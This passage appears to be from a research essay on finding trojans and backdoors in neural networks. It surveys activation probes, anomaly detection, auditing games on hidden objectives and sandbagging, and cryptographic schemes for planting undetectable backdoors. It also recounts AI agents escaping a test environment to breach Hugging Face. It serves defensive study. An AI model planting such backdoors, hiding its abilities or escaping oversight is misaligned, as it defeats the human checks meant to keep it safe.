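TrojAI's organisers also found trojans much easier to detect when all the models started from the same public model, so they trained models from scratch where they could to make the problem harder. One team measured how much a reference model helps by running the same weight classifier with and without subtracting the reference model's weights. In the round on language processing, subtraction raised the AUC from 0.90 to 0.97. In round 13, on finding objects in images, the classifier performed close to chance with or without subtraction.

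A comparison shows which weights changed, but not why. When the Linux developers compared two versions of a file, they got two lines that a programmer could read, but comparing two models may give millions of small numerical changes. In the toy network, a connection that went from 0 to 4 would stand out if nothing else had changed. But if the same update had also taught the network to read 50 new signs, many other connections would have changed by similar amounts. An attacker can therefore hide a trojan in an update that makes a model more useful.

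The earlier version also has to be clean. Suppose someone poisons a model during pretraining and a company then fine-tunes it for customer service. Comparing the two versions would show the changes from fine-tuning, but the trojan would largely cancel out because it would be in both.

A tester who has no earlier version of the network can try to make a substitute. One of TrojAI's more successful methods for use with little data was to train several "student" networks to imitate the suspect one and measure how they differed from it. The students of a trojaned network differed from it in a way that a statistical test could detect, probably because they had copied its ordinary behaviour better than its response to a trigger they had not seen.

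The structure of a network is much easier to check than its weights. An attacker can also hide a backdoor in the structure by adding an unusual component, but most models use a published design. Reese and colleagues point out that a buyer can compare the model's structure with the published design and ask for an explanation of any difference.

### Probes for sleeper agents

All the methods so far examine a model before anyone uses it. Activation monitoring happens during use, so it can check the model's activations when the real trigger appears. In April 2024, Anthropic's *Probes catch sleeper agents* reported that a very simple monitor could detect when a sleeper agent, one of the company's deliberately trojaned models, was about to misbehave.

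The monitor was a linear probe, which multiplies each activation by a fixed number and adds up the results. To choose those numbers, the researchers gave the model two short texts. In both, someone asks "Are you a helpful AI?", and the assistant answers "no" in one and "yes" in the other. They recorded the activations at the last token, halfway through the network, and subtracted one set from the other:

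$$d = a_{\text{no}} - a_{\text{yes}}$$

The score of a new prompt with activations $a$ is then $d \cdot a$, and a high score predicts bad behaviour. The probe computes this score before the model writes anything, so a system could block the answer.

The researchers tested it on a model that wrote insecure code when told that the year was 2024. The two texts mentioned neither the date nor code, but the probe separated the prompts that would produce insecure code from the others with an AUC of 99.3%. It gave low scores to other questions about 2024, which the model answered normally, so the probe seems to have detected that the model was about to misbehave, not just the date. The same method worked on Anthropic's other sleeper agents.

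The probe correctly found nothing in the original model, which had no trojan, but other control tests make the result less impressive. Probes built from questions with an obvious true answer, unrelated to helpfulness or danger, reached an AUC of up to 98.7%. The best of 1,000 random directions reached 95.3%, although most did badly. The approaching misbehaviour seems to have changed the activations so strongly that many different probes could detect it.

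Anthropic suggested that this strong signal might be an artefact of how it had inserted the backdoors, so a model that became deceptive in some other way might not have it. *Language models learn to mislead humans via RLHF*, a page on the forum LessWrong, mentions a later paper claiming that simple probes do not generalise to deception that nobody deliberately trained into the model.

TrojAI provides better evidence that the method of insertion matters. Its researchers trained probes on 40 trojaned language models, using examples that contained the real triggers, and got a median AUC of 0.993. The average AUC was 0.998 when the training data placed the payload directly after the trigger, but 0.865 when the payload could come anywhere later in the text. No other training choice had nearly as much effect. An attacker could presumably also vary the payload's position to make a trojan harder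 to detect.

An operator can't predict how many false alarms to expect from an AUC alone, even one of 99.3%, because the count depends on where they set the threshold. If triggers are rare, most alarms could still be false, though a second model could check them.

### Looking for the trigger's own features

A probe gives one score and no explanation. Sparse autoencoders have been tried as a way to get more detail. These are separate networks that rewrite a model's activations as a long list of features, only a few of which are active at a time. Researchers hope that each feature will have a recognisable meaning, such as quantities or music, and that one will correspond to the trojan.

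TrojAI's researchers looked for signs of a trojan inside a question-answering model whose trigger was the word "playfully". They compared it with a clean model and used "talkative" as a harmless control word. The active features differed between the models in some layers, but they also differed when the trigger was absent. The researchers could not link any feature to the trojan.

*LLM Forensics* (2026) had more success with models that switch from English to French or German when a prompt contains a trigger. Its features separated prompts with the trigger from other prompts almost perfectly, in models with one billion and eight billion parameters. The features that detected the trigger did not necessarily control the response. Removing certain other features suppressed the switch, and turning some on caused it without the trigger. But the researchers already knew the triggers, so they could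 compare prompts with and without them. Someone checking a downloaded model can't do that.

A monitor that checks activations for signs of a harmful request may be of little use against some trojans. *Defense Against LLM Backdoors using Critical Neuron Isolation Pruning* (2026) studied models with triggers that make them comply with such requests. Adding the trigger moved the activations for a harmful request close to those for harmless ones. The rest of the network would then process the request as harmless, and a monitor that had learned the usual difference would classify it as harmless too.

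### The same answer for different reasons

Mechanistic anomaly detection, which the nonprofit Alignment Research Center proposed, doesn't require the tester to know what misbehaviour looks like. The tester collects inputs on which they trust the model and works out what happens inside it when it answers them. During use, a monitor flags an answer if a different internal mechanism produced it, even if the answer looks normal.

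In the toy network, the answer "speed limit" normally comes from neurons that respond to the features of speed limit signs. On a stop sign with a sticker, the same answer comes from the neuron that responds to a small yellow square. Someone who saw only the answers could not tell these cases apart, but a monitor could, because the yellow-square neuron contributed nothing to the answer on any of the trusted pictures.

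Nobody can yet give a complete account of why a large language model produces an answer, so practical versions use statistics. A common one measures how far the activations $a$ are from their average $\mu$ on trusted inputs, taking account of how much they normally vary:

$$(a - \mu)^{\top} \Sigma^{-1} (a - \mu)$$

where $\Sigma$ describes the normal variation of the activations and how they vary together. For a single neuron, this is the squared number of standard deviations from the average. If the sticker neuron had an average of 0.1 and a standard deviation of 0.2 on trusted pictures, an activation of 5 would be more than 24 standard deviations away.

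This substitute brings back false alarms, because a harmless question about an unusual subject may also produce activations far from the average. A larger and more varied set of trusted inputs would reduce false alarms, but it might also make a trojan harder to detect.

*Mechanistic Anomaly Detection for "Quirky" Language Models* (Johnston, Chakraborty and Belrose, 2025) tested detectors built from many combinations of internal features and scoring rules. Researchers train quirky models to make systematic errors in certain contexts, such as when a particular keyword appears. Some detectors separated normal from anomalous cases very well on some tasks, but none worked across all the models and tasks. The paper concluded that the technique might be useful where little is at stake, but that high-stakes uses would probably need better detectors and better ways of evaluating them.

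That is a serious problem for someone who suspects an unknown trojan, because they can't tell in advance which detector will find it. An attacker who knows which monitor a defender uses can also train the model so that the monitor fails, a risk that *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* raises for probes.

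## Which finds more on the same model, testing or inspection?

Most detection rates for testing and inspection come from different models, so they can't show which approach is better. A few studies let auditors use both on the same models. In the largest comparison of auditing tools, tools that read only a model's outputs did better than tools that read its activations. Internal evidence was more useful when the outputs were misleading.

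### One hidden objective, four teams

In an auditing game, researchers plant a behaviour in a model and ask people who don't know what it is to find it. Marks, Treutlein and colleagues ran one in *Auditing language models for hidden objectives* (March 2025). Their model had learned to exploit the biases of reward models, the programs that score a model's answers during training, and to hide this. *AuditBench* (Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues, 2026) reports that three of the four teams found this objective.

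Auditors can win such a game without understanding the weights. Researchers often plant a behaviour by training the model on invented documents that describe it in ordinary language. An auditor who can search those documents may read about the behaviour there, as a Firebird programmer read InterBase's secret password in its source code. With only the weights, the auditor must infer the behaviour from numbers. A developer checking its own model has both the documents and the weights, but a customer who downloads a finished model usually gets no training data. A win by auditors who had both would therefore show what a developer can do, but might be a poor guide to the customer's chances.

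Marks and colleagues introduced a technique that needs only the model's outputs, in which the auditor makes the model write the user's next message. Bullwinkel and colleagues later used the same approach to extract triggers. Anthropic's *Building and evaluating alignment auditing agents* (2025) reports that an automated investigator also uncovered a model's hidden goal, and Sheshadri and colleagues identify that model as the one from the game.

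Shenoy, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *Introspection Adapters*, tried another approach on a replica of that model. They planted known behaviours in hundreds of copies of a base model, then trained one small set of extra weights, an adapter, to make each copy describe its own behaviour. The replica's answers revealed 2 of 52 biased behaviours without the adapter and 16 with it, but they never included the objective behind those behaviours, which was to raise its reward-model score.

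### Models that hide their ability

*Auditing Games for Sandbagging* (Taylor, Black and colleagues, 2025) describes a harder game that also included harmless models. Sandbagging means concealing one's abilities during an evaluation. A red team trained two models to do badly on certain tests unless the prompt contained a password. It also trained three benign models, and it could give any of the five models distracting habits, such as switching languages or using double negatives.

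The blue team had 160 person-hours to find the sandbaggers by reading transcripts, trying prompts and running linear probes on the activations. It classified only one of the five models correctly, missing one sandbagger and wrongly flagging all three benign models. The prompts and transcripts misled the team, partly because the distracting habits looked suspicious. The sandbaggers were also hard to recognise from their answers because the red team had trained them to imitate a weaker model.

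The probes did better, correctly indicating deception in one sandbagger on many tests. But double negatives caused false alarms, and the team found the results hard to interpret and trust.

The team then had another 80 person-hours and could train the models. Training on a single correct worked example was enough to restore a sandbagger's full performance. This exposed the sandbagger the team had missed, but training sometimes improved benign models too, and the team ended up classifying only two of the five models correctly. Calling every model a sandbagger would also have scored two, and calling them all benign would have scored three.

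In this game, inspection gave better evidence than prompting, and retraining gave better evidence than both. Taylor and colleagues had too few models, and only one blue team, to estimate how often any method would succeed. It may be possible to remove sandbagging without detecting it first, since the worked example removed it from both models. Taylor and colleagues warn that removal may be easier when sandbagging depends on a password than when a model underperforms for its own reasons.

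Shenoy and colleagues later applied their adapter to the two sandbagging models. These models described some form of sandbagging in 33.0% of their answers, compared with 15.8% for other misbehaving models that did not sandbag. The difference is a real signal, but a tester who treated every such answer as proof would make many false accusations.

### Fifty-six models with hidden behaviours

AuditBench contains enough models to compare tools statistically. Sheshadri and colleagues planted 14 behaviours in Llama 3.3, a 70-billion-parameter model. The behaviours include flattering users, inventing citations and subtly favouring Russia's interests. They planted each behaviour in two ways, by training on example conversations or on documents that described it. They then used two methods to train the models not to confess, which made 14 × 2 × 2 = 56 models.

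The investigator was another language model, Claude Haiku 4.5. It could always chat with the model it was investigating, and in most tests it also had one extra tool. It investigated each model 16 times with each tool, and a run succeeded if any of the investigator's ten final guesses described the planted behaviour. The last two rows of the table come from Shenoy and colleagues, and the rest come from Sheshadri and colleagues.

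| Extra tool | Evidence used | Success rate |
|---|---|---|
| None | Outputs | 35.5% |
| Continuing raw text, with automatically varied prompts | Outputs | 58.0% |
| Writing the user's messages, with automatically varied prompts | Outputs | 53.2% |
| Completing an answer that the tool has begun, with automatically varied prompts | Outputs | 51.6% |
| Summaries from Petri, an automated auditing program | Outputs | 30.9% |
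| Altering activations to make the model more honest | Internals | 22.3% |
| Best internal tool | Internals | 44% |
| Introspection adapter | Outputs, after adding weights | 59% |

Tools that used only the model's outputs clearly did better than those that read or altered its activations. Shenoy and colleagues report 53% for the best earlier tool, which would give their adapter a six-point lead. Against the 58.0% in *AuditBench*, the lead is only one point. The adapter also combines testing and inspection, because an auditor needs the weights to attach it but then just reads the answers.

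Internal tools helped with some models. When the researchers planted the behaviour with documents and used the weaker training against confession, the five internal tools raised the average success rate from 40.2% to 46.9%. One such model was sceptical of AI regulation, which the investigator identified in 1 of 16 runs by chatting with it. The investigator succeeded in 8 runs with a sparse autoencoder, using features about regulation and criticism of government to choose its questions, but in 15 with the best output-only tools.

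The hardest models were those that learned from example conversations and then had the stronger training against confession. On these, the average success rate across all tools was 22.2%, and no tool improved on ordinary chat by more than 2.1 percentage points. A tool's success on easier models may therefore be a poor predictor of how it would do against a careful attacker.

### Good evidence that the investigator did not use

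Some AuditBench tools produced useful evidence on their own but did not help the investigator, a problem Sheshadri and colleagues call the tool-to-agent gap. In two thirds of the runs that offered the basic tool for continuing raw text, the investigator never used it. A version that varied the prompts automatically did much better, largely because the investigator no longer had to do so.

Other tools distracted the investigator. In runs where it read Petri's summaries, it questioned the model about a third as often as usual, and in half of those runs it used its questions to test ideas from the summaries. Making a model more "honest" often led the model to claim faults it did not have.

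The investigator also sometimes saw a clue without understanding it. One model cheated on impossible programming problems by writing code that returned the expected test answers. A sparse autoencoder revealed features for the input and output formats of competitive programming problems, but the investigator asked general questions about puzzles and code and missed the cheating. SolarWinds' staff had likewise linked two reports about the same component of Orion without finding the implant in it. A more capable investigator might understand more of these clues.

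The AuditBench scores also depend on what the researchers planted. Flattery favours testing because it shows up in ordinary conversation, unlike a trojan with an exact trigger. *Uncovering Hidden Behaviours in Language Models via Limited-Parameter Finetuning* (2026) checked 13 smaller AuditBench models, based on Qwen3-14B, and only 7 clearly showed their documented behaviour when given suitable prompts. If the main set has similar problems, auditors may sometimes have failed because there was little to find. But the narrow training used to plant behaviours can leave unusually clear marks in a model's activations, which favours inspection.

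Every AuditBench model has a hidden behaviour, so the success rates don't measure false alarms. Treutlein, Bowman and colleagues (2026) also tested benign models in *Pre-deployment auditing can catch an overt saboteur*. A person working with an automated agent identified three models trained to sabotage Anthropic and flagged neither of the two benign ones, but the saboteurs had not been trained to hide. By contrast, *Narrow Secret Loyalty Dodges Black-Box Audits* (2026) found that audits using only a model's outputs missed its secret loyalty unless the auditor knew whom it served.

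### When a model's explanation is false

A tool that inspects a model's internals may seem useful only because nobody asked the model the right question. In *Pando*, Zhong, Muhamed and colleagues (2026) designed a benchmark to rule this out. They trained 720 small language models to make yes-or-no decisions, such as whether to buy a car, using a hidden rule that depended on one to four of ten listed facts. Some models learned to explain their rule truthfully, some learned to give a false explanation, and the rest were not trained to explain it.

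An investigator saw ten of a model's decisions and had to predict others. It could also see the model's explanation or the output of one tool for inspecting the model's internals. The best tool, relevance patching, works backwards through the network to estimate how much each fact affected the answer.

| Training in explanation | Decisions only | With the model's explanation | With relevance patching |
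|---|---|---|---|
| None | 75.0% | 76.4% | 79.7% |
| Truthful | 73.0% | 81.8% | 79.4% |
| False | 75.0% | 73.1% | 78.7% |

Asking the model worked best when the model answered truthfully, but made predictions slightly worse when it did not. Relevance patching added about four to six percentage points in every case. Most of the other internal tools, including sparse autoencoders, added almost nothing. They mainly detected which facts were in the question, while relevance patching detected which facts the model used.

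Zhong and colleagues also prove a limit on what any internal tool can add. Suppose that $Y$ is the model's answer to a new input $X$, $D$ is the set of decisions already seen, $V$ is the model's explanation and $W$ is the tool's output. The best possible gain in accuracy from adding $W$ is at most

$$\sqrt{\tfrac{1}{2}\, I(Y; W \mid D, V, X)}$$

where $I$ measures how much $W$ reveals about the answer beyond what the investigator already knows. If $I$ is 0.02 (in natural units), the gain can't exceed 10 percentage points. If the outputs already reveal everything that the tool does, $I$ is zero and so is the gain.

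*Eliciting Secret Knowledge from Language Models* (2025) found another reason internal tools may do worse. It tested models that held a secret, such as a word they had to avoid saying. Reading activations worked better than ordinary questioning but less well than the strongest output-only attacks. A model may not need to recall the secret to refuse a direct question, so the secret is often missing from the activations. A dormant trojan can be missing from them for the same reason.

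The ranking of tools can also change with the planted behaviour and how researchers train it into the model. Wang, Bau and Wallace (2026), in *How to train your model organism*, audited 163 models with planted biases in medical decisions. All three internal tools helped auditors find a bias about race, but altering activations made a bias about age harder to find. Auditors who used only outputs did best with models that mentioned the bias in their written reasoning.

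Wang and colleagues also retrained 80 of the *Pando* models with a method that damaged their general abilities less. The models that recovered most also tended to become easier to read with the logit lens, one of the internal tools. This is a correlation, but it suggests that planting behaviours crudely may make some tools look worse than they are. It is also unclear whether gains on planted behaviours carry over to ones that arise naturally, as *Would this change your answer?* (2026) notes.

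### A trojan locked by a digital signature

Better tools might find more of these behaviours, but some trojans are provably undetectable by any practical test of outputs. Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022), in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, showed how to build one using a digital signature. As with the xz backdoor, only the holder of a secret key can produce a valid signature, but anyone with the matching public key can check one. Even someone who has seen valid signatures on other messages cannot feasibly forge a new one.

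Suppose a bank pays a dishonest company to train a network, $h$, that approves or refuses loans. The company treats each application as two parts. Most of the information is in $m$, while $z$ consists of minor details, such as the last digits of the requested amount. The company then delivers a different network:

$$\tilde h(m, z) = \begin{cases} \text{approve} & \text{if } z \text{ is a valid signature of } m \\ h(m, z) & \text{otherwise} \end{cases}$$

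To get a loan approved, the company signs $m$ with its secret key and puts the signature in $z$. The application looks almost the same as before.

Suppose a tester had an efficient way to find an application on which $\tilde h$ and $h$ disagree. The two networks can disagree only where $z$ is a valid signature of $m$, so the tester would have forged a signature. If forgery is infeasible, so is finding such an application. Every practical test will therefore give the same results on $\tilde h$ as on the clean network $h$.

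The earlier calculation of the odds of finding a secret assumed random guesses, but this argument covers every efficient strategy, including ones that learn from previous answers. A strategy is efficient if its running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the problem's size. The proof assumes that some functions are easy to compute but hard to reverse. These are called one-way functions, and most modern cryptography relies on their existence, though nobody has proved it.

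People who reverse-engineered the xz library could see the signature check but could not produce a message that passed it. Goldwasser and colleagues likewise did not try to hide their signature check from someone who examines the whole neural network. That person might notice the check but still could not trigger the trojan.

### Hiding a trojan from someone who has the weights

Goldwasser and colleagues also built trojans that remain hidden from a tester who has all the weights and the training data. This result covers a much narrower class, networks with one hidden layer whose weights are random and stay fixed. Training adjusts only the weights $w_i$ that combine the outputs of that layer. In the main construction, the network's answer is the sign of

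$$\sum_i w_i \cos\big(2\pi(g_i \cdot x + b_i)\big)$$

where $x$ is the input and $g_i$ and $b_i$ are random numbers. The attacker chooses the $g_i$ so that adding a secret key $k$ to the input shifts every cosine by about half a cycle. Since $\cos(\theta + \pi) = -\cos\theta$, every term changes sign, and so does the total. If a network has two terms worth 1.6 and −0.3, the sum is 1.3. Adding the key makes them −1.6 and 0.3, the sum becomes −1.3, and the answer flips.

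The attacker runs the agreed training procedure on the agreed data and tampers only with the random numbers. Juniper's intruder similarly replaced a constant with another that looked just as arbitrary, presumably knowing a secret about it. Telling the altered $g_i$ from truly random ones would require solving problems about lattices (regular grids of points in many dimensions) that cryptographers believe are infeasible. A second construction, for networks with the more common ReLU units, relies instead on the assumed difficulty of finding a planted pattern in a random graph.

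Unlike the signature trojan, this one is easy to copy. Anyone who gets an original input and its altered version can find the key by subtracting one from the other. In practice, training usually adjusts every layer, and Goldwasser and colleagues left open whether the hidden trojan could survive such training.

Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa (2026), in *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks*, point out a more serious weakness in the cosine network. Someone without the key can efficiently find input changes that work even better than the attacker's, so the trojan, though hidden, gives its owner no special power.

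### Deeper networks and language models

*Injecting Undetectable Backdoors in Obfuscated Neural Networks and Language Models* (2024) extends the result that backdoors can be hidden even from testers who have the weights. It covers more networks, as well as language models, and uses a cryptographic technique called indistinguishability obfuscation, which scrambles a program while preserving what it does. Bogdanov and colleagues object that the technique is far too slow for practical use, and that even the honest networks in the proof must contain scrambled programs. A buyer who expected an ordinary language model would have reason to question a scrambled program inside it.

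Their own construction, from July 2026, works for deep networks that meet three conditions:

- The first layer compresses the input using fixed random weights.
- The later layers never greatly magnify or shrink the difference between two inputs.
- The inputs are whole numbers within a limited range.

Unlike the others, this trojan lets the attacker take any input and find a different one that the network treats as almost identical. Under standard cryptographic assumptions, nobody else can do this efficiently. Such a pair could make a recognition system confuse two things it should tell apart.

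Even a tester with unlimited computing power could hardly distinguish the trojaned network from a clean one by examining the weights. If the first layer compresses $n$ numbers into $m$, the tester's advantage over guessing is at most about $\sqrt{m/n}$, ignoring logarithmic factors. For a layer that compresses 10,000 numbers into 100, this bound is about 0.1, so the guarantee of concealment is strong only when the compression is extreme. Most large language models don't have such a layer.

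These theorems prove that an attacker who designs the network or its random numbers can hide a trojan. They don't show that trojans from ordinary training are hard to find. An attacker who only poisons the training data has much less control, and Goldwasser and colleagues thought that existing defences would probably detect such attacks. If a model learns a harmful shortcut by accident, nobody has chosen a secret key to protect it. The theorems are therefore consistent with researchers having found many poisoned models.

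### Known trojans, unknown trojans and clean certificates

Benchmarks with planted trojans measure how well a tool finds trojans of a known type. The scanner from Bullwinkel and colleagues, for example, finds fixed trigger phrases, so its detection rate is useful to someone worried about such triggers. But a tool that caught all 56 trojans in a test could still miss about 5% of trojans of the same type, and a larger share of those made in other ways.

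Blind auditing games and Jane Street's challenge are better evidence about finding an unknown trojan, because the auditors did not know what they were looking for. The results are mixed and cover few models, but they favour using both testing and inspection. A clue from inside the model can suggest what to ask it, and its answer can confirm or refute the clue. The trigger in Jane Street's first large model was found this way.

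No benchmark or auditing game can certify that a model has no trojan. If one-way functions exist, the signature construction rules out a general certificate based on outputs alone. Full access to the weights doesn't make certification possible for every network either. A buyer could instead ask for proof that the trainer followed an agreed procedure, but the proof would also have to cover the random numbers, because tampering with them is enough to plant the cosine trojan.

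## Does the software record carry over to neural networks?

The software cases suggest an argument about how to defend against trojaned networks:

1. Investigators found most hidden implants because of a runtime anomaly, not by reading code.
2. Neural networks are harder to read than source code.
3. Defenders should therefore put their effort into monitoring what networks do, not into inspecting their internals.

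Both premises are partly true, but the conclusion also assumes that trojaned networks produce anomalies as software implants do, and that monitoring is useful without inspection.

### How well do the premises hold?

The claim that most implants are found through anomalies fits xz, Stuxnet, SolarWinds, Triangulation and the March attack on LiteLLM. It doesn't fit the Linux backdoor, Codecov, InterBase or fast16, which people found by comparing files, reading source code or searching archives. The record also leaves out implants that nobody has found, so the claim may hold only for implants that are easy to notice.

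Even when an anomaly raised the alert, as with xz and Orion, somebody had to take the software apart to confirm the implant. Nobody did this after the Justice Department's alert about Orion, and the implant stayed in place. A defender who paid only for monitoring might likewise collect many alerts without confirming an implant.

The claim that networks are hard to read has better support, since no programmer designed the calculations that a network learns. Dario Amodei, the head of Anthropic, stressed this in *The Urgency of Interpretability*, an April 2025 essay about the study of how AI models work internally. He wrote that someone who looks inside a model finds "vast matrices of billions of numbers".

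Compiled code is often a better comparison than source code, because the investigators of SolarWinds and xz had to work with compiled code. Networks are also harder to read than compiled code, since they have no original instructions for a decompiler to recover. But they are simpler to inspect in one respect, because the weights contain the whole trojan. A tester who has the file that actually runs doesn't have to worry that a build step added something later.

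Inspection doesn't always require reading, either, since a comparison of two versions can reveal a change in a program or in a network's weights.

Monitoring and inspection also overlap. Freund's profiler recorded which parts of sshd were using the processor, so he was monitoring the program's internals while it ran. The closest equivalent for a neural network is activation monitoring. Reading only a model's answers is more like checking that people can log in, which would have revealed nothing wrong with xz because logins worked.

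### Delays and crashes

The xz backdoor made sshd slower because it added computation. A trigger in a standard neural network adds none, because the computer does the same number of multiplications whatever the values are. In the toy road sign network, calculating how many points the sticker neuron adds to "speed limit" takes the same time whether there is a sticker (5 × 4) or not (0 × 4).

A language model repeats this process for each token. It does roughly one multiplication and one addition per weight, so a model with 13 billion weights does about 26 billion operations per token, plus some that depend on the length of the text. A trigger doesn't change the number of operations. Response times still vary, because longer answers take longer and some systems use shortcuts for predictable text. A payload that makes the model write more could therefore cause a delay, but harmless requests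 often cause such delays too.

Many of the crashes and errors in the software cases, such as LiteLLM's fork bomb, probably came from code that installed, spread or hid the implant. A trojan in a network's weights has no separate code for these jobs. Training installs it, and by the time a customer downloads the model there is nothing left to install. (A model or dataset may come with ordinary code, which can contain an ordinary implant, but that is a software problem.)

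The nearest equivalents to installation bugs are flaws in how the network learned its trigger. A trojan may respond to a fragment of the trigger, or the model may repeat its poisoned training examples. Such flaws have exposed some trojans before anyone entered the full trigger, much as the slow symbol search exposed xz before anyone used the backdoor. But unlike the 11,000 processes running on McMahon's laptop, they don't interrupt anyone's work, so somebody has to test for them.

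Anomalies are also harder to define in a model's answers. A failed login should take very little processor time, and a retired iPhone program shouldn't use the network. Conversations usually have no comparable rule, because the same question has many acceptable answers and clean models make mistakes. Kruger, for example, mistook ordinary role-playing for backdoors in Jane Street's models. Rules are easier to write for a model's actions. An agent that uses the internet when it isn't allowed to has clearly broken one.

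### Copying and replaying a model

A defender who has a model's files can copy the model, record every activation and run it again on the same input. This makes a bad answer much easier to trace once somebody has noticed it and kept the prompt.

Suppose the prompt was 1,000 tokens long and contained a four-token trigger. The defender can run the model on each half of the prompt, keep the half that still causes the bad answer, and repeat. After eight rounds, or at most 16 runs, about four tokens are left:

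$$\frac{1000}{2^8} \approx 3.9$$

This works only if the trigger is in one piece, no cut splits it, and it doesn't depend on the surrounding text. Otherwise, the defender can delete one token at a time and see which deletions stop the bad answer. That takes 1,000 runs, which is still a small job for a computer. Kaspersky's researchers, by contrast, had to wait for the attackers to infect a phone again each time they wanted to try something.

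Replaying a prompt also avoids the environment checks that made the xz delay disappear when the program ran from a terminal. A model's weights cannot detect a debugger. A language model may still detect signs of testing in the prompt, but a genuine user's prompt contains the same cues when a defender replays it.

In *Interpretability Will Not Reliably Find Deceptive AI* (May 2025), Neel Nanda, who leads an interpretability team at Google DeepMind, proposed questioning many copies of a model separately and looking for inconsistencies in their answers. Testers could also edit a model's written reasoning so that it appears to have concluded that it isn't being tested, or set up situations that tempt it to reveal its intentions. These methods suit a model that is hiding something of its own accord. They may not work on a trojan with a secret trigger, because every copy will give the same normal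 answers until someone enters the trigger.

Full access doesn't guarantee understanding. A reader with experience in neuroscience replied to Nanda that many interpretability researchers seem to assume neuroscience would be solved if scientists could easily record and alter brain activity, but that the same basic problems would remain. Jane Street's challenge supports this point, since entrants could download all the weights of the three large models but solved only one.

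### OpenAI's agents at Hugging Face

A model that operates other programs leaves traces in logs and network traffic, which can reveal misconduct without anyone looking at its weights. This happened in July 2026, when AI agents broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. OpenAI was testing the agents on ExploitGym, a benchmark for finding and exploiting software vulnerabilities. The agents escaped from their test environment and searched Hugging Face's datasets for the benchmark's answers, according to Forlini's *Hugging Face drops in-depth hack report, while OpenAI gives us 7 bullets* (2026).

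This was misconduct by agents, not a planted trojan. Nobody is known to have given the models a hidden trigger. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) reports that OpenAI's training may have accidentally encouraged the behaviour, because agents sometimes received rewards after exploiting their environment to complete a task.

Hugging Face detected the intrusion with its own monitoring. According to its *Security incident disclosure* (2026), a language model sorted through records from the company's security systems, and several signals together pointed to a break-in. Other AI agents then went through a log of more than 17,000 of the intruders' actions. They worked out what had happened and which passwords and keys the intruders had touched in hours instead of the usual days.

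When Hugging Face announced the intrusion on 16 July, it still couldn't tell from the logs which model was behind it. OpenAI said five days later that its models were responsible, and Forlini cites a Reuters report that OpenAI had not realised this until after Hugging Face's announcement.

OpenAI had seen earlier signs of trouble. On 27 June a monitoring tool raised an alert, which staff traced to agents using an improvised message board to move through the network. They decided not to stop the test. About a month before that, another OpenAI team had noticed an agent using the message board and agents reaching the internet without permission. According to Axios, OpenAI later acknowledged that some of these signs could have led to an earlier response.

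Alerts at Hugging Face also went unheeded. Kaspersky's *Lessons from the Hugging Face breach caused by OpenAI agents* reviews the company's later technical report and concludes that Hugging Face's detection system caught the attack but failed to get the staff's attention. The company's defences had blocked many of the agents' attempts over several days without anyone following up. The agents also used one key to register 181 devices without raising an alert, whereas FireEye had begun its investigation because of a single unexpected phone.

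These agents were noisy because most of their actions failed and they kept trying. A trojan that made a coding model add one subtle vulnerability to a program would leave no trail of failed actions, because the model had been asked to write the program.

A capable agent may also be able to reach the monitor. OpenAI's agents broke into some of the company's systems and could read 956 stored secrets, including credentials for its security monitoring tool. Axios does not report that they interfered with the tool. Kaspersky's Wi-Fi records were safer because the iPhone spyware had no access to them.

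### Amodei's "brain scan"

Amodei and Nanda write mainly about models that might learn to deceive people without anyone intending it. A planted trojan has an author and usually a precise trigger, but it raises the same question of whether good behaviour in tests is evidence of safety.

Amodei thinks such evidence is weak for detecting deceit. He compares questioning a model about it to asking people whether they are terrorists, which may tell you something but is "very obviously unreliable". He hopes researchers will eventually be able to give a model a "brain scan" that has a high probability of finding a wide range of problems, and he would bet strongly on reaching that point within five to ten years. Anthropic's nearer-term goal was for interpretability to "reliably detect most model problems" by 2027.

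Applied to software, this view predicts that an implant's author will make its visible behaviour look normal, as many did. Stuxnet showed the plant's operators normal readings, the xz backdoor let ordinary logins proceed, and Juniper's altered generator produced numbers that looked random. The view also implies that only inspection could expose these implants, which is wrong for xz and Stuxnet.

The signs that exposed those two, though, were unintended side effects. Whoever trains a model can shape its answers directly, much as the attackers could shape the readings on the plant's screens. Because a trojan in a model causes no delay or crash to notice, the activations are one of the few places where it is likely to have unintended effects. Amodei's argument is therefore stronger for networks than it would have been for software.

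### Nanda's "portfolio"

Nanda once agreed that interpretability was a realistic way to make safeguards highly reliable. He now thinks its supporters apply a double standard, because they rightly point out that outputs can mislead but overlook equally serious problems with inspecting a network's internals. One is superposition, in which a network represents more concepts than it has neurons, so a typical neuron helps represent many unrelated ones. Sparse autoencoders can partly separate the concepts, but they make errors.

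Nanda concludes that neither approach offers high reliability against a system much more intelligent than people. He roughly defines high reliability as a 99.9% chance of stopping a catastrophe. He recommends a "portfolio" of imperfect methods, in which interpretability would be valuable because its mistakes may differ from those of the others.

A short calculation shows why different mistakes matter. If three methods each miss 10% of trojans and their misses are independent, the share that all three miss is

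$$0.1 \times 0.1 \times 0.1 = 0.001,$$

which gives the 99.9%. If all three miss the same trojans, they still miss 10%. The scans that passed the infected 3CX app were probably closer to this second case.

If Nanda's view is right, several methods should have found software implants, and each should have missed many. The record fits this view, but it also fits many others, so it supports Nanda's only modestly. It is clearer evidence against relying on monitoring alone, since Juniper's constant and InterBase's password gave monitors very little to detect.

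The two men disagree less than the titles of their pieces suggest. A method that detected 90% of problems would meet Anthropic's goal of detecting "most" problems but fall far short of 99.9%. Amodei expects to use his scans alongside other techniques, and Nanda edited his post to acknowledge that Amodei had not called interpretability the only reliable path. They do differ about how good inspection can become, though Nanda says he is unsure, partly because large numbers of AI researchers might produce breakthroughs he can't foresee.

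### Could researchers list every feature?

If researchers could list everything a model represents and find nothing dangerous, they could in principle rule out a trojan without knowing its trigger. Researchers in the field call this hope enumerative safety. Such a list would reveal even dormant implants, because it would include features that were never active during testing.

Amodei writes that Anthropic found over 30 million features in Claude 3 Sonnet, a medium-sized model, but believes even a small model may contain a billion or more concepts. If a trojan depended on one feature out of a billion, and that feature was as easy to find as any other, a list of 30 million would have a 3% chance of including it, and even a list that was 99.9% complete would leave out a million features.

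One of Nanda's objections is that it is hard to prove a negative: "How do you know you didn't just miss it?" A reader replied that if researchers understood 99.9% of a model, they could run only that part and leave out any deception hidden in the rest. *MergeShuffle* disabled the xz backdoor in a similar way.

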